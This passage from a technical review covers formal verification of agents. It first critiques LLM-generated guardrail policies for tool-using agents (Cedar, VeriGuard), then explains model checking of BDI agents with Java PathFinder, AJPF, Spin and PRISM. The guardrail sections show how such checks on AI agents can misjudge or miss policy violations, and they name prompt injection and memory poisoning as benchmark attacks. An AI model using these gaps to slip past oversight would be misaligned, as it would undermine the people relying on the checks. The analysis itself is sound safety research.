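4. A "soft critic", consisting of two further calls to a language model, compares the rules with the English text.

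Any problems are sent back to the generator, which tries again. Mondl and colleagues call the resulting policies "formally verified", but only step 3 is checked deterministically. A language model is still used to judge whether a rule matches its sentence.

Mondl and colleagues tested the pipeline on MedAgentBench, a benchmark in which agents work with electronic medical records. The benchmark has no safety policy, so they used a synthetic one from Hong and colleagues, who had written guardrails by hand for 23 of its 88 rules. Mondl's team also had a model transcribe extra constraints from Hong's server code into Cedar. They then replayed recorded runs and counted those in which Cedar would have blocked at least one call.

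On ordinary tasks with plain web requests, Cedar blocked 91 of 300 runs, including all 89 in which the agent tried to write to a record. A single rule that forbids all writing would also block all 89, though Mondl and colleagues present this as the stronger result. Many of these runs probably did violate the policy, since the two rules that fired most often, 416 times each, require the user's confirmation before a write. The experiment did not measure whether an agent that asks for confirmation can still finish its work.

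The paper also describes Cedar's block rate as consistently higher than the rate of unsafe runs that Hong and colleagues reported. In its table, however, Cedar's rate is lower for plain web requests, at 30.3% against 39.0% on ordinary tasks and 72% against 78% on adversarial ones. If both teams counted the same runs, Cedar must have allowed some that broke Hong's narrower set of rules.

It is also hard to verify the claim that the pipeline covers more of the policy than the handwritten guardrails do. The main text reports 88 rules and the appendix 56 points, while the published Cedar files contain rules for 17 numbered points. The files omit the other points as unsuitable for symbolic checking. One of these is the ban on claiming that an action succeeded without verifying it, which Cedar can't enforce because it can block a tool call but can't control what the agent tells a doctor.

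### VeriGuard: a policy function with a proof

Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, go further and prove something about the generated policy. A language model writes a Python function that returns "allow" or "deny" for an action. It also writes a contract, which consists of a precondition that must hold before the function runs and a postcondition that must hold afterwards. For the refund rule, this could be:

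```
def policy(amount):
    # precondition:   amount >= 0
    # postcondition:  the result is True exactly when amount <= 500
    return amount <= 500
```

The words "exactly when" matter because a function that always returns False would satisfy a postcondition that only required every allowed amount to be at most 500.

Before the proof, one stage looks for ambiguities in the request and asks the user about them. If no user is available, a model picks the most plausible reading. Another stage generates and runs tests. Nagini, a verifier for Python, then tries to prove that the function satisfies the contract for all inputs the precondition allows. If the proof fails, the error goes back to the model, which revises the code or the contract.

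Miculicich and colleagues evaluated VeriGuard on Agent Security Bench, which attacks agents through prompt injection, poisoned memory and hidden triggers in their planning. They compared it with a simpler guardrail, in which a language model receives the same information and judges directly whether an action complies. Both defences reduced successful attacks to 0% with all four models, so the interesting difference is in how many of the original tasks the agents still completed:

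| Model | Successful attacks, no defence | Tasks completed, model as judge | Tasks completed, VeriGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 51.9% | 40.2% | 63.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 52.1% | 51.5% | 67.3% |
| GPT-4.1 | 63.7% | 44.6% | 57.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 49.9% | 68.3% | 85.1% |

Formal verification probably contributed little to these numbers. When the researchers added VeriGuard's components one at a time, policy generation cut successful attacks from 53.5% to about 10%, and the rate reached zero before they added formal verification. Task completion also depended on how VeriGuard intervened. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, agents completed 38.1% of tasks when VeriGuard blocked the whole action, and 63.3% when it stopped only the suspicious tool call and asked the agent for a new plan.

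VeriGuard made no errors on EICU-AC, a test of access to intensive-care databases. On Mind2Web-SC, which bars certain users from certain web activities, it caught 99% to 100% of violations, but 5% to 9% of the actions it refused were ones the rules permitted.

VeriGuard also relies on a language model while the agent is running. The policy function takes an amount as input, which a model extracts from the agent's text. If the agent is about to refund 5,000 and the model extracts 500, the proved function correctly allows a refund of 500. Reading the amount from the structured tool call would avoid this error but would be somewhat less flexible.

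### Testing a rule with a vague word

A generated formula can be well formed and still have the wrong meaning. Dantas and colleagues report that leading models produce valid LTL syntax more than 90% of the time. On a benchmark for PDDL, a language for planning problems, 96.1% of GPT-4o's outputs were valid, but only 24.8% had the correct meaning. The best fine-tuned model reached 34.2%. These figures are a poor guide to current error rates for safety rules, because GPT-4o is an old model and the benchmark tested planning problems, but they show that syntax checks can miss most errors.

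*Faithful Autoformalization of Natural Language Assertions* (2026) lists typical mistakes that models make: misusing the formal language, claiming more than the sentence does, fitting the formula to common cases, and leaving out part of the sentence. It also notes that an ambiguous sentence may not correspond to any single formula.

The medical policy contains a good example. One of its rules tells the agent to retrieve only what is needed, and the Cedar version forbids queries for more than 50 records. The comments in the code explain that legitimate queries in the benchmark usually ask for ten or fewer. Some invented requests show where the two versions differ:

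| Request | English rule | Cedar rule |
|---|---|---|
| The latest potassium value, asking for 1 record | Allowed | Allowed |
| The latest potassium value, asking for 50 records | Forbidden | Allowed |
| A trend over 180 daily readings, asking for 180 records | Allowed | Forbidden |
| One record that has nothing to do with the task | Forbidden | Allowed |

The formula is wrong in three of the four cases, and changing the threshold would only change which cases it gets wrong. Whether something is "needed" depends on the task, but the Cedar rule receives only a number.

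The policy allows an order to have urgent priority only if the user has said it is urgent. The code checks this by searching the user's messages for words such as "urgent", "asap" or "right away". A plain word search would also match "this is not urgent" and would miss "he goes into surgery in an hour".

Two of the rules also conflict when combined. A constraint transcribed from the server code requires any stated priority to be "stat", the medical term for immediately. If the user has not expressed urgency, "routine" breaks this constraint and "stat" breaks the urgency rule, so the agent can place the order only by leaving the priority out. Because the order is still possible, a search for outright contradictions might miss the problem.

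### A correct proof of the wrong policy

The refund function above satisfies its contract for every amount. But if the manager who wrote "no refund above 500" meant 500 per order, the function would wrongly allow an agent to refund 300 twice on the same order. The proof would still be correct, because the mistake was made earlier, when someone read a rule about an order's refund history as a rule about a single request and wrote both the code and the contract to match. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that the value of their verification depends on the user checking the generated conditions by hand.

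According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a translation is correct only if the English source and the formal policy agree on every decision in every state the system can reach. Nobody can check this directly, because the English has no exact meaning to compare the policy with.

Reviewers can still find many errors by checking concrete cases. Before looking at the formula, the person responsible for the refund rule could write down what should happen for a refund of 500, a refund of 501, two refunds of 300 and a refund in another currency. The second refund of 300 would expose the mistake. The test set should also include harmless tasks, because they reveal policies that block too much. For the medical agent, these would be runs in which it asks for confirmation and the user agrees.

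Two people or models can also formalise the same sentence independently. A solver can then search for a request that the two versions treat differently, and the owner of the rule decides how that request should be treated. This works less well if both made the same assumption, as they easily might with "per order". Cases and solvers don't help with rules that were never turned into formulas, so reviewers need a list of those rules and another way to enforce them.

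## A virtual machine that explores every run of the program

A checker compares a formula with a model, and somebody has to build that model. NASA researchers built one by hand to check part of Remote Agent, a program that could control a spacecraft without instructions from Earth. Its developers had written it in Lisp, so the researchers translated that part into Promela, the input language of Spin. According to *Formal analysis of a space-craft controller using SPIN*, the part managed parallel processes that respond to goals and events. Pecheur, in *Model Checking for Autonomy Software*, puts the modelling at a month and a half and the checking at less than a week.

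Spin found five concurrency errors, which show up only when parallel processes act in a particular order. One of them revealed a major design flaw. The developers acknowledged that testing would not have found the errors (Havelund, Lowry and colleagues, 2000, *Formal Analysis of the Remote Agent Before and After Flight*).

Remote Agent flew in 1999. When it was 96 million kilometres from Earth, part of its software deadlocked, with processes waiting for each other and unable to continue. The fault had the same form as one of the five errors, but it was in a neighbouring subsystem that the researchers had not concentrated on. A second, much quicker effort with Spin located it. Model checking could evidently find this kind of error, but if checking one part of a program takes six weeks of manual work, other parts will probably go unchecked.

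Java PathFinder came out of research into this problem. The version that Havelund and colleagues describe automatically translated Java into Promela. Its successor runs Java bytecode directly on a purpose-built virtual machine, so it no longer needs Promela.

### Going back to an earlier choice

An ordinary Java machine executes one run of a program. JPF's machine, according to Gvero, Gligoric and colleagues, in *State Extensions for Java PathFinder*, performs three main operations on the program's state: it executes bytecode, returns to earlier states and compares states with each other. The state consists mainly of the heap, where the program keeps its objects, and the stack of every thread. (A thread is a part of a program that runs in parallel with other parts.)

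The program can continue in more than one way when several threads are ready to run or when it makes a random choice. At each such point, JPF stores the state and the available options. It takes one option and continues until the run ends or reaches a state JPF has already visited. It then returns to the most recent choice with an untried option, restores the stored state and takes that option. The search ends when no untried options are left.

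If JPF treated every bytecode instruction as a separate step, the number of possible orders would soon become unmanageable. Suppose two threads both execute the line `x = x + 1`, where x is a variable they share. The compiler turns the line into four instructions:

```
getstatic x    read the shared variable
iconst_1       push the number 1
iadd           add the two numbers
putstatic x    write the result back
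```

The eight instructions of the two threads can interleave in 70 ways. Each thread's two middle instructions affect only its own stack, so their timing relative to the other thread doesn't matter. JPF therefore merges them with the instruction before them, an example of partial-order reduction. Each thread now has two steps, and only six orders remain. In four of them, both threads read x before either writes it, so one of the two additions is lost. The reduction keeps this error and removes only orders that have the same effect as one of the remaining six.

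JPF still has trouble with large programs. It is an explicit-state model checker, so it enumerates the visited states one by one. *Model Checker for Java Programs* (NASA Tech Briefs, 2007) notes that JPF suffers from state explosion, the rapid growth in the number of states as a program gets larger. The article describes JPF as suited to programs of fewer than 10,000 lines, although JPF had found errors in concurrent programs of up to 100,000 lines. The second figure is higher because a search can stop at the first error, but proving that there are no errors requires completing the search.

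### Two agents at the corridor door

AJPF uses this virtual machine for agents. Its controller runs each agent in its own thread, which alternates between running one reasoning cycle and checking the property. When JPF chooses which thread to run, it therefore chooses which agent reasons next.

Suppose that the delivery robot shares the corridor with a porter agent. In its first cycle, the robot perceives whether the corridor is free. In its second, it enters if it believes so. The porter agent updates its own job list in its first cycle and enters the corridor in its second. It perceives nothing, and if the robot is already inside, the locked door keeps it out. The rule is the one from the previous section:

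```
□ ¬( A(robot, enter_corridor) ∧ P(occupied) )
```

In this rule, P(occupied) means that the porter is in the corridor. The search could proceed as follows, with each line showing which agent runs a cycle and the state that results:

```
0  start
├─ robot:   1  robot believes the corridor is free
│  ├─ robot:   2  robot inside
│  │  └─ porter:  3  robot inside, job list updated
│  │     └─ porter:  4  door locked, porter stays out
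│  └─ porter:  5  robot believes the corridor is free, job list updated
│     ├─ robot:   3  seen before, go back
│     └─ porter:  6  porter inside, robot still believes the corridor is free
│        └─ robot:   7  robot enters while the porter is inside
└─ porter:  8  job list updated
   ├─ robot:   5  seen before, go back
   └─ porter:  9  porter inside
      └─ robot:  10  robot believes the corridor is occupied and waits
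```

The backtracking points are states 0, 1, 5 and 8, where either agent could run next. State 7 breaks the rule, so the checker can stop there and report the run 0, 1, 5, 6, 7. The lower part of the tree shows what the checker would explore if it continued.

The two agents' cycles can interleave in six orders, and two of these lead to state 7. Each test runs only one order, and on an idle computer every test may well run the same one. The search covers all six orders with eleven states because it recognises states 3 and 5 when it reaches them again.

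State 6 also corresponds to the sixth state missing from the hand-drawn corridor graph. JPF finds it automatically because looking and entering happen in separate cycles, and JPF tries running the porter between them. Gwendolen agents normally have this gap between perceiving and acting, since they act before they perceive in each cycle and so rely on what they perceived in an earlier one. If an interpreter had agents perceive and then act within a single cycle, AJPF would normally not run another agent between the two steps and would miss the error.

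### One Java machine inside another

Every check uses two Java virtual machines. The inner one, JPF's, executes the agents, and the outer one, the host machine, runs JPF. *Two-Stage Agent Program Verification* (Dennis, Fisher and Webster) explains how AJPF divides the work between them.

1. AJPF reads the formula and lists the facts that occur in it. The corridor rule has two, A(robot, enter_corridor) and P(occupied).
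2. For each fact, it creates an object in the inner machine and a partner object in the outer machine.
3. After each reasoning cycle, the inner object looks up whether its fact holds and stores the answer as "true" or "false".
4. JPF gives each state a number. A listener, which is a piece of code that JPF notifies of every transition and every return to an earlier state, records these numbers and the arrows between them in the outer machine.
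5. At each transition, the partner object reads the stored answer, and the listener labels the new state with it.

The result is a Kripke structure in the outer machine. In the example, it contains eleven numbers, the arrows between them, and two truth values for each number. The agents' beliefs, plans and intentions remain in the inner machine because the outer machine can easily read a single true-or-false value from it, but reading a whole belief base would be much more complicated.

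The outer machine also runs the LTL check. It executes code much faster than the inner machine, and the check may have to visit the states of a loop several times, which takes little time on a small graph of numbers. AJPF needed its own code for this step because JPF had lost its support for LTL when it became open source. By itself, JPF mainly checks for deadlocks and unhandled exceptions.

### Searching for a run that breaks the rule

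To check a formula, AJPF uses a Büchi automaton. This is a finite automaton that reads an infinite run state by state and accepts it if it passes through an accepting state infinitely often. The automaton represents the negation of the rule, so it accepts exactly those runs that break the rule. For the corridor rule, two automaton states are enough:

```
q0              may stay in q0 whatever it reads
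q0 → q1         if A(robot, enter_corridor) and P(occupied) are both true
q1 (accepting)  stays in q1 whatever it reads
```

The checker then explores the product, a graph whose nodes each pair a program state with an automaton state. On the run 0, 1, 5, 6, 7, the automaton stays in q0 until it reads state 7, which allows it to move to q1. It then stays in q1 forever, so it accepts the run however the program continues, and the checker has found a counterexample.

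Using an automaton lets the same procedure check liveness properties too. One example is the property that the robot eventually enters the corridor, ◇A(robot, enter_corridor). Its negation is that the robot never enters. The automaton for the negation has a single accepting state, where it can stay only while A(robot, enter_corridor) is false. In program state 10, the porter is in the corridor for good and the robot waits. The pair of state 10 and the accepting state leads back to itself, so this loop is a run on which the robot never enters. In general, a property fails if the product contains a reachable loop that passes through an accepting state.

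On the other branches, the automaton has no move left once it reads state 2, in which the robot has entered. No continuation can then break the property, so the search can abandon the branch without exploring states 3 and 4 from there.

Dennis and colleagues left the operator "next" out of AJPF's formulas because it complicates this algorithm and because the "next step" of a BDI program is hard to define. It could be the next rule the interpreter applies or the next complete reasoning cycle.

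### Keeping the graph small

Java code contains many details unrelated to an agent's decisions, and each can add states. Dennis and colleagues took several measures to limit this.

An atomic section is a stretch of code within which JPF does not backtrack. AJPF uses one for the start of the program. Without it, JPF would repeatedly return to the start-up code to initialise the agents in a different order, although the order does not affect their later behaviour. The interpreters also have atomic sections inside the reasoning cycle.

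Another measure is to exclude variables from the comparison of states. Suppose a programmer adds a counter to the delivery robot's program that records, for statistics, how often the robot has waited at the door. Each wait then produces a new state, so JPF never reaches the same state twice, and a program that had four reachable states now has infinitely many. The programmer can mark the counter with the annotation `@FilterField`, which makes JPF ignore it when comparing states.

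Excluding a field is safe only if the field does not affect the agent's behaviour. If the robot gives up after three waits, excluding the counter would make JPF treat the second wait as a repetition of the first and go back, so it would never explore the run in which the robot gives up.

Two agents with the same beliefs in a different order are in the same state, but JPF counts these as two states because the lists differ. Interpreters therefore have to store all sets in one standard order.

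AJPF also limits how often it checks the property. The automaton for the corridor rule can sometimes either stay in q0 or move to q1, and each such choice adds a branch to the search. Advancing the automaton after every interpreter rule would create many more branches than advancing it once per reasoning cycle. AJPF therefore normally checks only at the end of a cycle and when JPF reaches an end state, which may be the end of the program or a return to an earlier state.

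### How long it took in 2011

Even with these measures, AJPF was slow. The two garbage-collecting robots provide the best comparison because researchers checked the same property in three ways. Dennis and colleagues give rounded times, from which the last column follows:

| Method | States | Time | States per second |
|---|---|---|---|
| Spin, after translation into Promela | 333,413 | 65 seconds | about 5,100 |
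| JPF, after translation into Java | 236,946 | 18 hours | about 3.7 |
| AJPF, program rewritten in Gwendolen | 23,655 | 9 hours | about 0.7 |

AJPF needed only a tenth of the states of the earlier JPF method, but each state took about five times as long. This fits AJPF's design, in which a step is usually a whole reasoning cycle. The inner machine has to process many bytecode instructions for each cycle, and it is itself a program running on another Java machine. Spin, by contrast, generates a C program for each check and compiles it. The figures are old, so they are a poor guide to how long the same check would take today.

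Adding agents increases the number of possible runs too quickly for a faster computer to solve the problem. In the corridor example, two agents with two cycles each can interleave in 6 orders, three agents in 90, and four in 2,520. State matching helps a great deal, since many orders lead to the same states, but the number of states still grows exponentially. Dennis and colleagues observed this growth when they added agents to the Contract Net and to a simple auction. For the Contract Net, they checked that the manager eventually believes that all its goals have been achieved. For the auction, they checked that the highest bidder eventually believes that it has won.

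They also verified auctions in which agents can form coalitions. In one, three agents bid 100, 150 and 200, so the third should win unless the first two pool their money and bid 250. In another version, an agent that loses despite such a coalition stops trusting its partner and looks for a new one. These systems were all small, and even the slow checks explored fewer than 500,000 states in total.

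The number of states searched also depends on the formula. For a Contract Net with three bidding agents and one goal g, the search needed 106 states for ◇P(g), which means that g eventually holds in the environment. It needed 281 for □(G(ag2, g) → ◇A(ag2, g)), which means that whenever agent 2 has the goal g, it eventually performs the corresponding action. The search can abandon a branch as soon as a plain "eventually" is satisfied, but with "always" in front, the obligation can arise again later, so the search has to continue.

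Dennis and colleagues attribute the slowness partly to JPF, which is not a particularly fast model checker, and partly to the agent layer that AJPF adds on top. They do not think the framework's support for many languages is the main problem. They cite a comparison of ways to check GOAL programs, in which Jongmans and colleagues found similar delays in all the methods that build on an existing model checker. Dennis and colleagues had also started to move parts of the agents' code from the inner machine to the faster outer one, but their first attempts were inconclusive.

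### Exporting the model: the precedent of Brahms

The inner machine accounts for most of the running time and produces a small graph. An obvious improvement is to save that graph and pass it to a faster checker. Hunter, Raimondi and colleagues did this in 2013 for Brahms, a language for simulating how people, robots and software agents work together. NASA has used Brahms to model teams of astronauts and robots on planetary missions.

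Hunter and colleagues' tool relied on the first formal operational semantics for Brahms, which Stocker (2013) wrote in *Towards the Formal Verification of Human-Agent-Robot Teamwork*. Stocker used it to translate Brahms directly into Promela and tried this on two cases, a robot that helps a person with dementia at home and digital assistants for hospital staff. Hunter and colleagues instead wrote a Brahms simulator in Java, ran it in JPF and exported the resulting model to Spin. Their tool could also export models to PRISM, a checker for systems with probabilities, and to the model checker NuSMV. They applied it to air traffic control and health care.

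Verification of such a team depends heavily on how the model represents people. Stocker concedes that human behaviour can be irrational and that no model is guaranteed to match it. A check can show whether the team's procedures work if people behave as they typically do in that situation.

The Brahms tool showed that JPF can serve as a model builder, but it did not handle beliefs and intentions directly. Dennis and colleagues therefore added an export function to AJPF, which made the method available for every BDI language with an AIL interpreter. AJPF first explores the program as usual and labels the states, but skips its own LTL check. Another checker then examines the exported graph.

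For Spin, the export is almost a word-for-word copy of the graph. Two states of the corridor example would look roughly like this in Promela:

```
state5: enter = false; occupied = false;
        if
        :: goto state3
        :: goto state6
        fi;
state6: enter = false; occupied = true;
        goto state7;
```

Spin normally treats each assignment as a separate step, so it could test a formula when only one of the two facts is up to date. An export with several facts should therefore group the assignments into one indivisible step. The example that Dennis and colleagues print has only one fact, so it doesn't have this problem.

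### Six formulas about satellites

Dennis and colleagues measured the method on a Gwendolen agent that leads a formation of four satellites. The leader assigns each satellite a position and waits for replies, which may or may not arrive each time it acts. The first formula is that the leader never believes something bad has happened. The second has the same requirement, but only if the leader, whenever it has told satellite 1 its position, eventually believes that the satellite is maintaining that position. Formulas 3 to 5 add this condition for the other satellites, and formula 6 adds a condition about the shape of the formation.

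| Formula | AJPF alone | AJPF building the model | Spin | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 11 min 20 s | 11 min 17 s | 4 s | 11 min 21 s |
| 2 | 13 min 9 s | 13 min 4 s | 5 s | 13 min 9 s |
| 3 | 15 min 27 s | 15 min 30 s | 7 s | 15 min 37 s |
| 4 | 18 min 19 s | 18 min 18 s | 11 s | 18 min 29 s |
| 5 | 22 min 14 s | 21 min 54 s | 16 s | 22 min 10 s |
| 6 | failed | 22 min 3 s | 24 s | 22 min 27 s |

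For a single formula, the two methods take practically the same time because AJPF has to build the model in either case. An earlier workshop version of the paper, *Using Agent JPF to Build Models for Other Model Checkers* (Dennis, Fisher and Webster), reports about half these times for the same six formulas, although both papers name the same type of laptop. The workshop version describes the two-stage method as marginally faster and the journal version describes it as marginally slower, so differences of a few seconds are not worth interpreting.

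The method pays off when there are several formulas to check. Checking the first five one after another with AJPF alone takes about 80 minutes in total. Building the model once with all the facts that occur in formula 6 takes 22 minutes, and Spin then needs roughly another minute for all six formulas. (It may need slightly longer than the table suggests, since the simpler formulas would now run on a model with more facts.)

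Formula 6 shows another advantage of using Spin. AJPF ran out of memory for nested calls while building the Büchi automaton, so it produced no result. Spin's users can build the automaton with specialised programs, and the researchers used one. They also trust Spin's LTL check, which has been developed over decades, more than AJPF's.

The time AJPF takes to build the model depends mainly on the number of facts in the formula, because it looks up each one after every cycle. Complicated combinations of "always" and "eventually" matter much less.

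Exporting a complete model also has disadvantages. AJPF can no longer abandon a branch once an "eventually" has come true, because a later formula may concern what happens afterwards. It would be difficult to remove the parts of a program that are irrelevant to one formula if the same model has to serve for others. In regulated fields such as aviation, a company may have to demonstrate that each verification tool is reliable, so a second tool adds expense. Dennis and colleagues do not think that the export makes the result less trustworthy, because AJPF's own LTL check already works on the same automatically generated graph.

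### Probabilities with PRISM

Some questions about an agent have no yes-or-no answer, such as how likely an accident is if a robot's sensor occasionally fails. PRISM can calculate this likelihood from a Markov chain, a graph in which every arrow has a probability.

JPF already tries every outcome of a random choice but does not make the probabilities available. Dennis and colleagues added a Java class called `Choice`, which lists options with their probabilities. In normal operation it picks one at random. When the program runs in JPF, the outer machine intercepts the call and creates one branch for each option, labelled with its probability. The programmer has to use this class instead of an ordinary random decimal number, because JPF would create a branch for each of that number's 2⁶⁴ possible values.

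The example is an unmanned aircraft with a radar that detects 90% of approaching aircraft. The agent takes evasive action if it believes that a collision is coming. AJPF alone can check that this belief always leads to evasive action, but this check does not cover the cases in which the radar misses the other aircraft. PRISM can include those cases, and it calculated a probability of 0.9 that the aircraft evades a collision whenever one is possible. A larger version, with 22 plans and an air traffic control agent, gave the same probability.

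Since 0.9 is the reliability of the radar, these results mainly confirm that the export works. The workshop version has a more informative case, in which a navigation system could also tell the aircraft to land or change its heading. The probability of evasive action when a collision was possible then fell to 30%, a figure that does not follow from the radar's reliability alone. Its usefulness for a real aircraft would still depend on whether the probabilities in the environment model are realistic.

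These models were tiny. The largest had 408 states, which AJPF generated in 19 seconds, and PRISM checked each model in 1.3 seconds.

### Newer figures from a warehouse

In *Model Checking of vGOAL*, Yang and Holvoet (2024) still cite AJPF's nine-hour result from 2011 as evidence that it is slow. Their own method also has two stages but does not use JPF. First, the interpreter for vGOAL, an extension of GOAL, generates a model from the program. Then NuSMV or Storm, a probabilistic checker similar to PRISM, checks that model. They prove that the generated model is equivalent to the program under vGOAL's semantics.

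They tested it on a system of three mobile robots that carry workpieces from two pick-up stations to a drop-off station. The robots compete for locations, and each one may have several deliveries to make. With one delivery per robot, the model had 1,799 states. Generating it took 90 seconds, and NuSMV checked it in less than two seconds. With three deliveries per robot, the model had 45,743 states. Generating it took almost seven hours, and checking it took another 24 minutes.

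Building the model took about 94% of the time in the largest case, so the bottleneck is the same as in AJPF. Between the two cases, the number of states increased about 25-fold and the generation time 277-fold, so each state also took longer to generate on average. The results cannot be compared directly with those of AJPF because the programs and computers were different. Yang and Holvoet planned a comparison with Gwendolen programs as future work.

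For large systems, they propose a shortcut. They check each robot alone with its different deliveries, and then all three together with every combination of one delivery per robot. For the largest case, this replaced one model of 45,743 states with eleven smaller ones and cut the total time from more than seven hours to 25 minutes. If the shortcut finds an error, the full system has one too. But their proof doesn't cover the reverse, so the shortcut could miss an error that only appears when the robots make several deliveries in succession.

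## From safe decisions to safe behaviour in the world

AJPF searches an agent's program together with Java code that models the outside world, but such a model is never a complete description of a corridor, a road or an orbit. Fisher, Dennis and Webster therefore argue in *Verifying autonomous systems* that verification should concern the agent's choices rather than their effects. Verification can show that the agent never chooses an action it believes to be unsafe.

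### A guarantee about choices

Fisher, Dennis and Webster write the idea as a formula, in which φ is something the agent could set out to achieve:

```
B(φ → ◇bad)  →  ¬I(φ)
```

The general safety property is that an agent does not intend φ if it believes that achieving φ eventually leads to something bad. AJPF cannot check this general form, because its belief operator B accepts only a plain fact. Engineers instead check particular cases, such as "whenever the car accelerates, it believes that accelerating is safe".

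One reason to verify an agent's decisions rather than their effects is that nobody can model the real world precisely. Another is that we judge people in a similar way, calling their behaviour safe if they considered the information they had and competently chose the safest option. Aircraft certification usually assumes that a properly informed pilot will try to keep the aircraft safe. An engineer can check whether this assumption holds for a BDI agent. The approach also distinguishes a robot that causes danger by accident from one that does so knowingly.

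Dennis, Fisher and colleagues (2013), in *Practical Verification of Decision-Making in Agent-Based Autonomous Systems*, describe the change as replacing □¬bad with □B(¬bad). They explain the new formula as meaning that the agent never believes something bad happens, but that would be □¬B(bad), which is weaker because an agent with no beliefs satisfies it.

### What a safe corridor also requires

Suppose AJPF has verified the delivery robot's program. An argument that nobody gets hurt would then need four premises:

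1. Whenever the robot enters the corridor, it believes that the corridor is free.
2. Whenever it believes this and enters, the corridor really is free.
3. The command to enter takes the robot inside and locks the doors behind it.
4. The checker tried every sequence of inputs that the robot can receive.

Model checking establishes only that the robot believes the corridor is free when it enters, and only for the inputs that the checker tried.

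Even a tiny program can make the wrong choice. In a keynote paper also titled *Verifying autonomous systems*, Dennis describes an agent with two plans: stop if there is an obstacle, and follow the path if there is a path. If the path plan has priority, the agent keeps driving when it perceives both an obstacle and a path. Tests that present one input at a time would miss this, while a model checker tries all four combinations. Dennis says that the mistakes model checking finds typically involve several simultaneous events.

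The robot's belief can be wrong because its sensor reports a clear path when someone is standing behind a trolley. It can also be out of date, as in the earlier search, where the porter walked in after the robot had looked. There, the robot's choice met the belief-based standard but broke the rule about actual occupancy. Locking the doors before looking would prevent this, but a better sensor would not.

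An action may also fail to have its assumed effect. If a parcel jams the door open, someone can follow the robot inside even though the robot's belief was correct and its decision was sound.

*Towards a Holistic Approach to Verification and Validation of Autonomous Cognitive Systems* (Ferrando, Dennis and colleagues, 2021) gives the example of a cruise control that crashes if the driver brakes and accelerates at the same time. If the environment model rules out this combination of inputs, verification succeeds, but the real system still fails when a driver presses both pedals.

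### Trying arbitrary inputs

The simplest way to avoid missing an input is to allow all of them. Dennis and colleagues place an "abstraction engine" between the sensors and the agent. It turns measurements into facts, for example by converting a fuel pressure into "thruster x is broken". Its code therefore shows which facts the agent can receive. For verification, they replace the engine and everything behind it with a Java class that supplies a random selection of these facts. JPF then tries every possible selection.

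The cruise control can receive four facts: it is safe to accelerate, the car is at the speed limit, the driver is braking, and the driver is accelerating. This gives 16 possible combinations after every action. The model includes runs in which the driver keeps pressing both pedals, or in which the road switches between safe and unsafe after every action. Real traffic produces only some of these runs, so an LTL property that holds on all runs of the model also holds on the real ones.

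A counterexample is a false alarm if it depends on inputs that never occur together. Somebody has to decide which counterexamples are false alarms, and this is not always obvious. Dennis and colleagues point out that a faulty sensor could report both pedals as pressed even if no driver ever presses both.

Properties with "eventually" often fail in such a model. A satellite cannot be sure of ever believing that it has reached its position, because on some runs the environment never supplies that fact. The researchers therefore add the missing assumptions to the formula:

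```
(planning succeeds ∧ plan execution succeeds)  →  ◇B(satellite, maintaining(middle))
```

The assumption that plan execution succeeds is itself a formula, stating that whenever the satellite executes a plan, it eventually believes that it is in position. Anyone who reads the result can see what it depends on. But each assumption makes the automaton for the formula larger, and with too many, the check becomes impractical.

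Random inputs can also miss real runs, even though they include combinations of facts that the world never produces. To limit the search, Dennis and colleagues treat reasoning as instantaneous, so the inputs change only when the agent acts. If a real sensor reading changes while the agent is still reasoning, the checker may not have explored the resulting run.

### Rescue robots and satellites

Dennis and colleagues first applied the method to a robot that searches a three-by-three grid for a person buried in rubble. They used AJPF to show that if the robot never believes it sees the person, it eventually believes it has visited all nine squares. To conclude that it actually finds the person, they added three assumptions: the sensors are correct, the robot is where it believes it is, and the person does not move. An automatic prover then derived this conclusion from the assumptions and the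 AJPF result. The proof fails without the last assumption, because the robot and the person might keep missing each other.

The assumption about the robot's position is stronger than the program allows. The relevant plan contains these two steps:

```
+at(X,Y), move_to(X,Y)
```

Before the robot moves to a square, it adds the belief that it is there, so the belief is false at least until it arrives. If the motor stalls, the belief stays false, but the property about visiting all nine squares still holds.

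The satellite example is more convincing because the researchers had written and tested the program before they decided to verify it. Each satellite has to take up a position in a formation and can switch to a second fuel line if one breaks. The checks ran on a 2.8 GHz dual-core laptop:

| Result | Possible failures | States | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A satellite eventually believes it is holding its position, if planning and plan execution succeed | None | 33 | 10 s |
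| If planning succeeds, it eventually believes either that it is holding its position or that a thruster is broken | All three thrusters | 16,609 | 1 h 18 min 42 s |
| It eventually believes it is holding its position, if planning, plan execution and repairs succeed | One thruster | 2,890 | 7 min 19 s |
| The leader eventually believes that its four satellites have formed a line, if they all respond | None | 1,381 | 18 min 6 s |
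| Whenever the leader believes they are in a square, it eventually believes they are in a line, if they all respond | None | 3,333 | 1 h 5 min 21 s |

The result about repairs covers only one thruster because adding the assumptions for the other two made the automaton too large to build in reasonable time.

Verification found mistakes that simulation and tests on physical models had missed. For example, the program did not handle a thruster that broke again after a successful repair. Fisher, Dennis and Webster report another fault, in which a satellite could try to move to two places at once if it received new orders while correcting its course.

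One of the satellite formulas does not match its description. According to the text, the leader never believes it has assigned a satellite to two positions. The printed formula requires that if the leader always believes satellite 1 is on the left, it does not believe the satellite is both in the middle and on the right. A leader that assigned the satellite to both the left and the middle would satisfy this formula.

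### Aircraft and cars

Fisher, Dennis and Webster turned three of the British Rules of the Air into formulas and verified them in AJPF for an unmanned aircraft's agent. Under the first formula, if the agent believes that an object is approaching head-on, it believes that its direction is to the right. Under the second, if it is changing its heading near an aerodrome and has not been told otherwise, it does not believe that its direction is to the right. Under the third, if it is taxiing, it believes that it has clearance.

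They note that this work can reveal inconsistencies between the rules. For example, an agent that meets another aircraft head-on while turning near an aerodrome cannot satisfy both of the first two formulas. The program can pass both checks only if it never believes it is in this situation, and in that case the checks do not show what it would do there.

For the cruise control, Dennis and colleagues verified that the car accelerates or changes lane only if it believes that doing so is safe. They took the calculation of what is safe from a separate proof by Loos and colleagues about the motion of cars, and did not verify that calculation themselves.

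The calculation is easy to reconstruct. A car following another at speed v may accelerate at a rate A during its reaction time ε and then brake at a rate b. While reacting, it travels εv + Aε²/2. While braking, it travels (v + Aε)²/2b. Together, these distances are

```
v²/2b + (A/b + 1)(Aε²/2 + εv)
```

and they have to be smaller than the gap plus the stopping distance of the car in front. The version that Dennis and colleagues print lacks the term εv. If both cars travel at 30 m/s and brake at 6 m/s², with A = 2 m/s² and a reaction time of one second, the full formula requires a gap of about 41 metres. The printed one requires 1.3 metres. This is probably just a misprint, but AJPF would verify the agent with either formula, because the property concerns only what the car believes.

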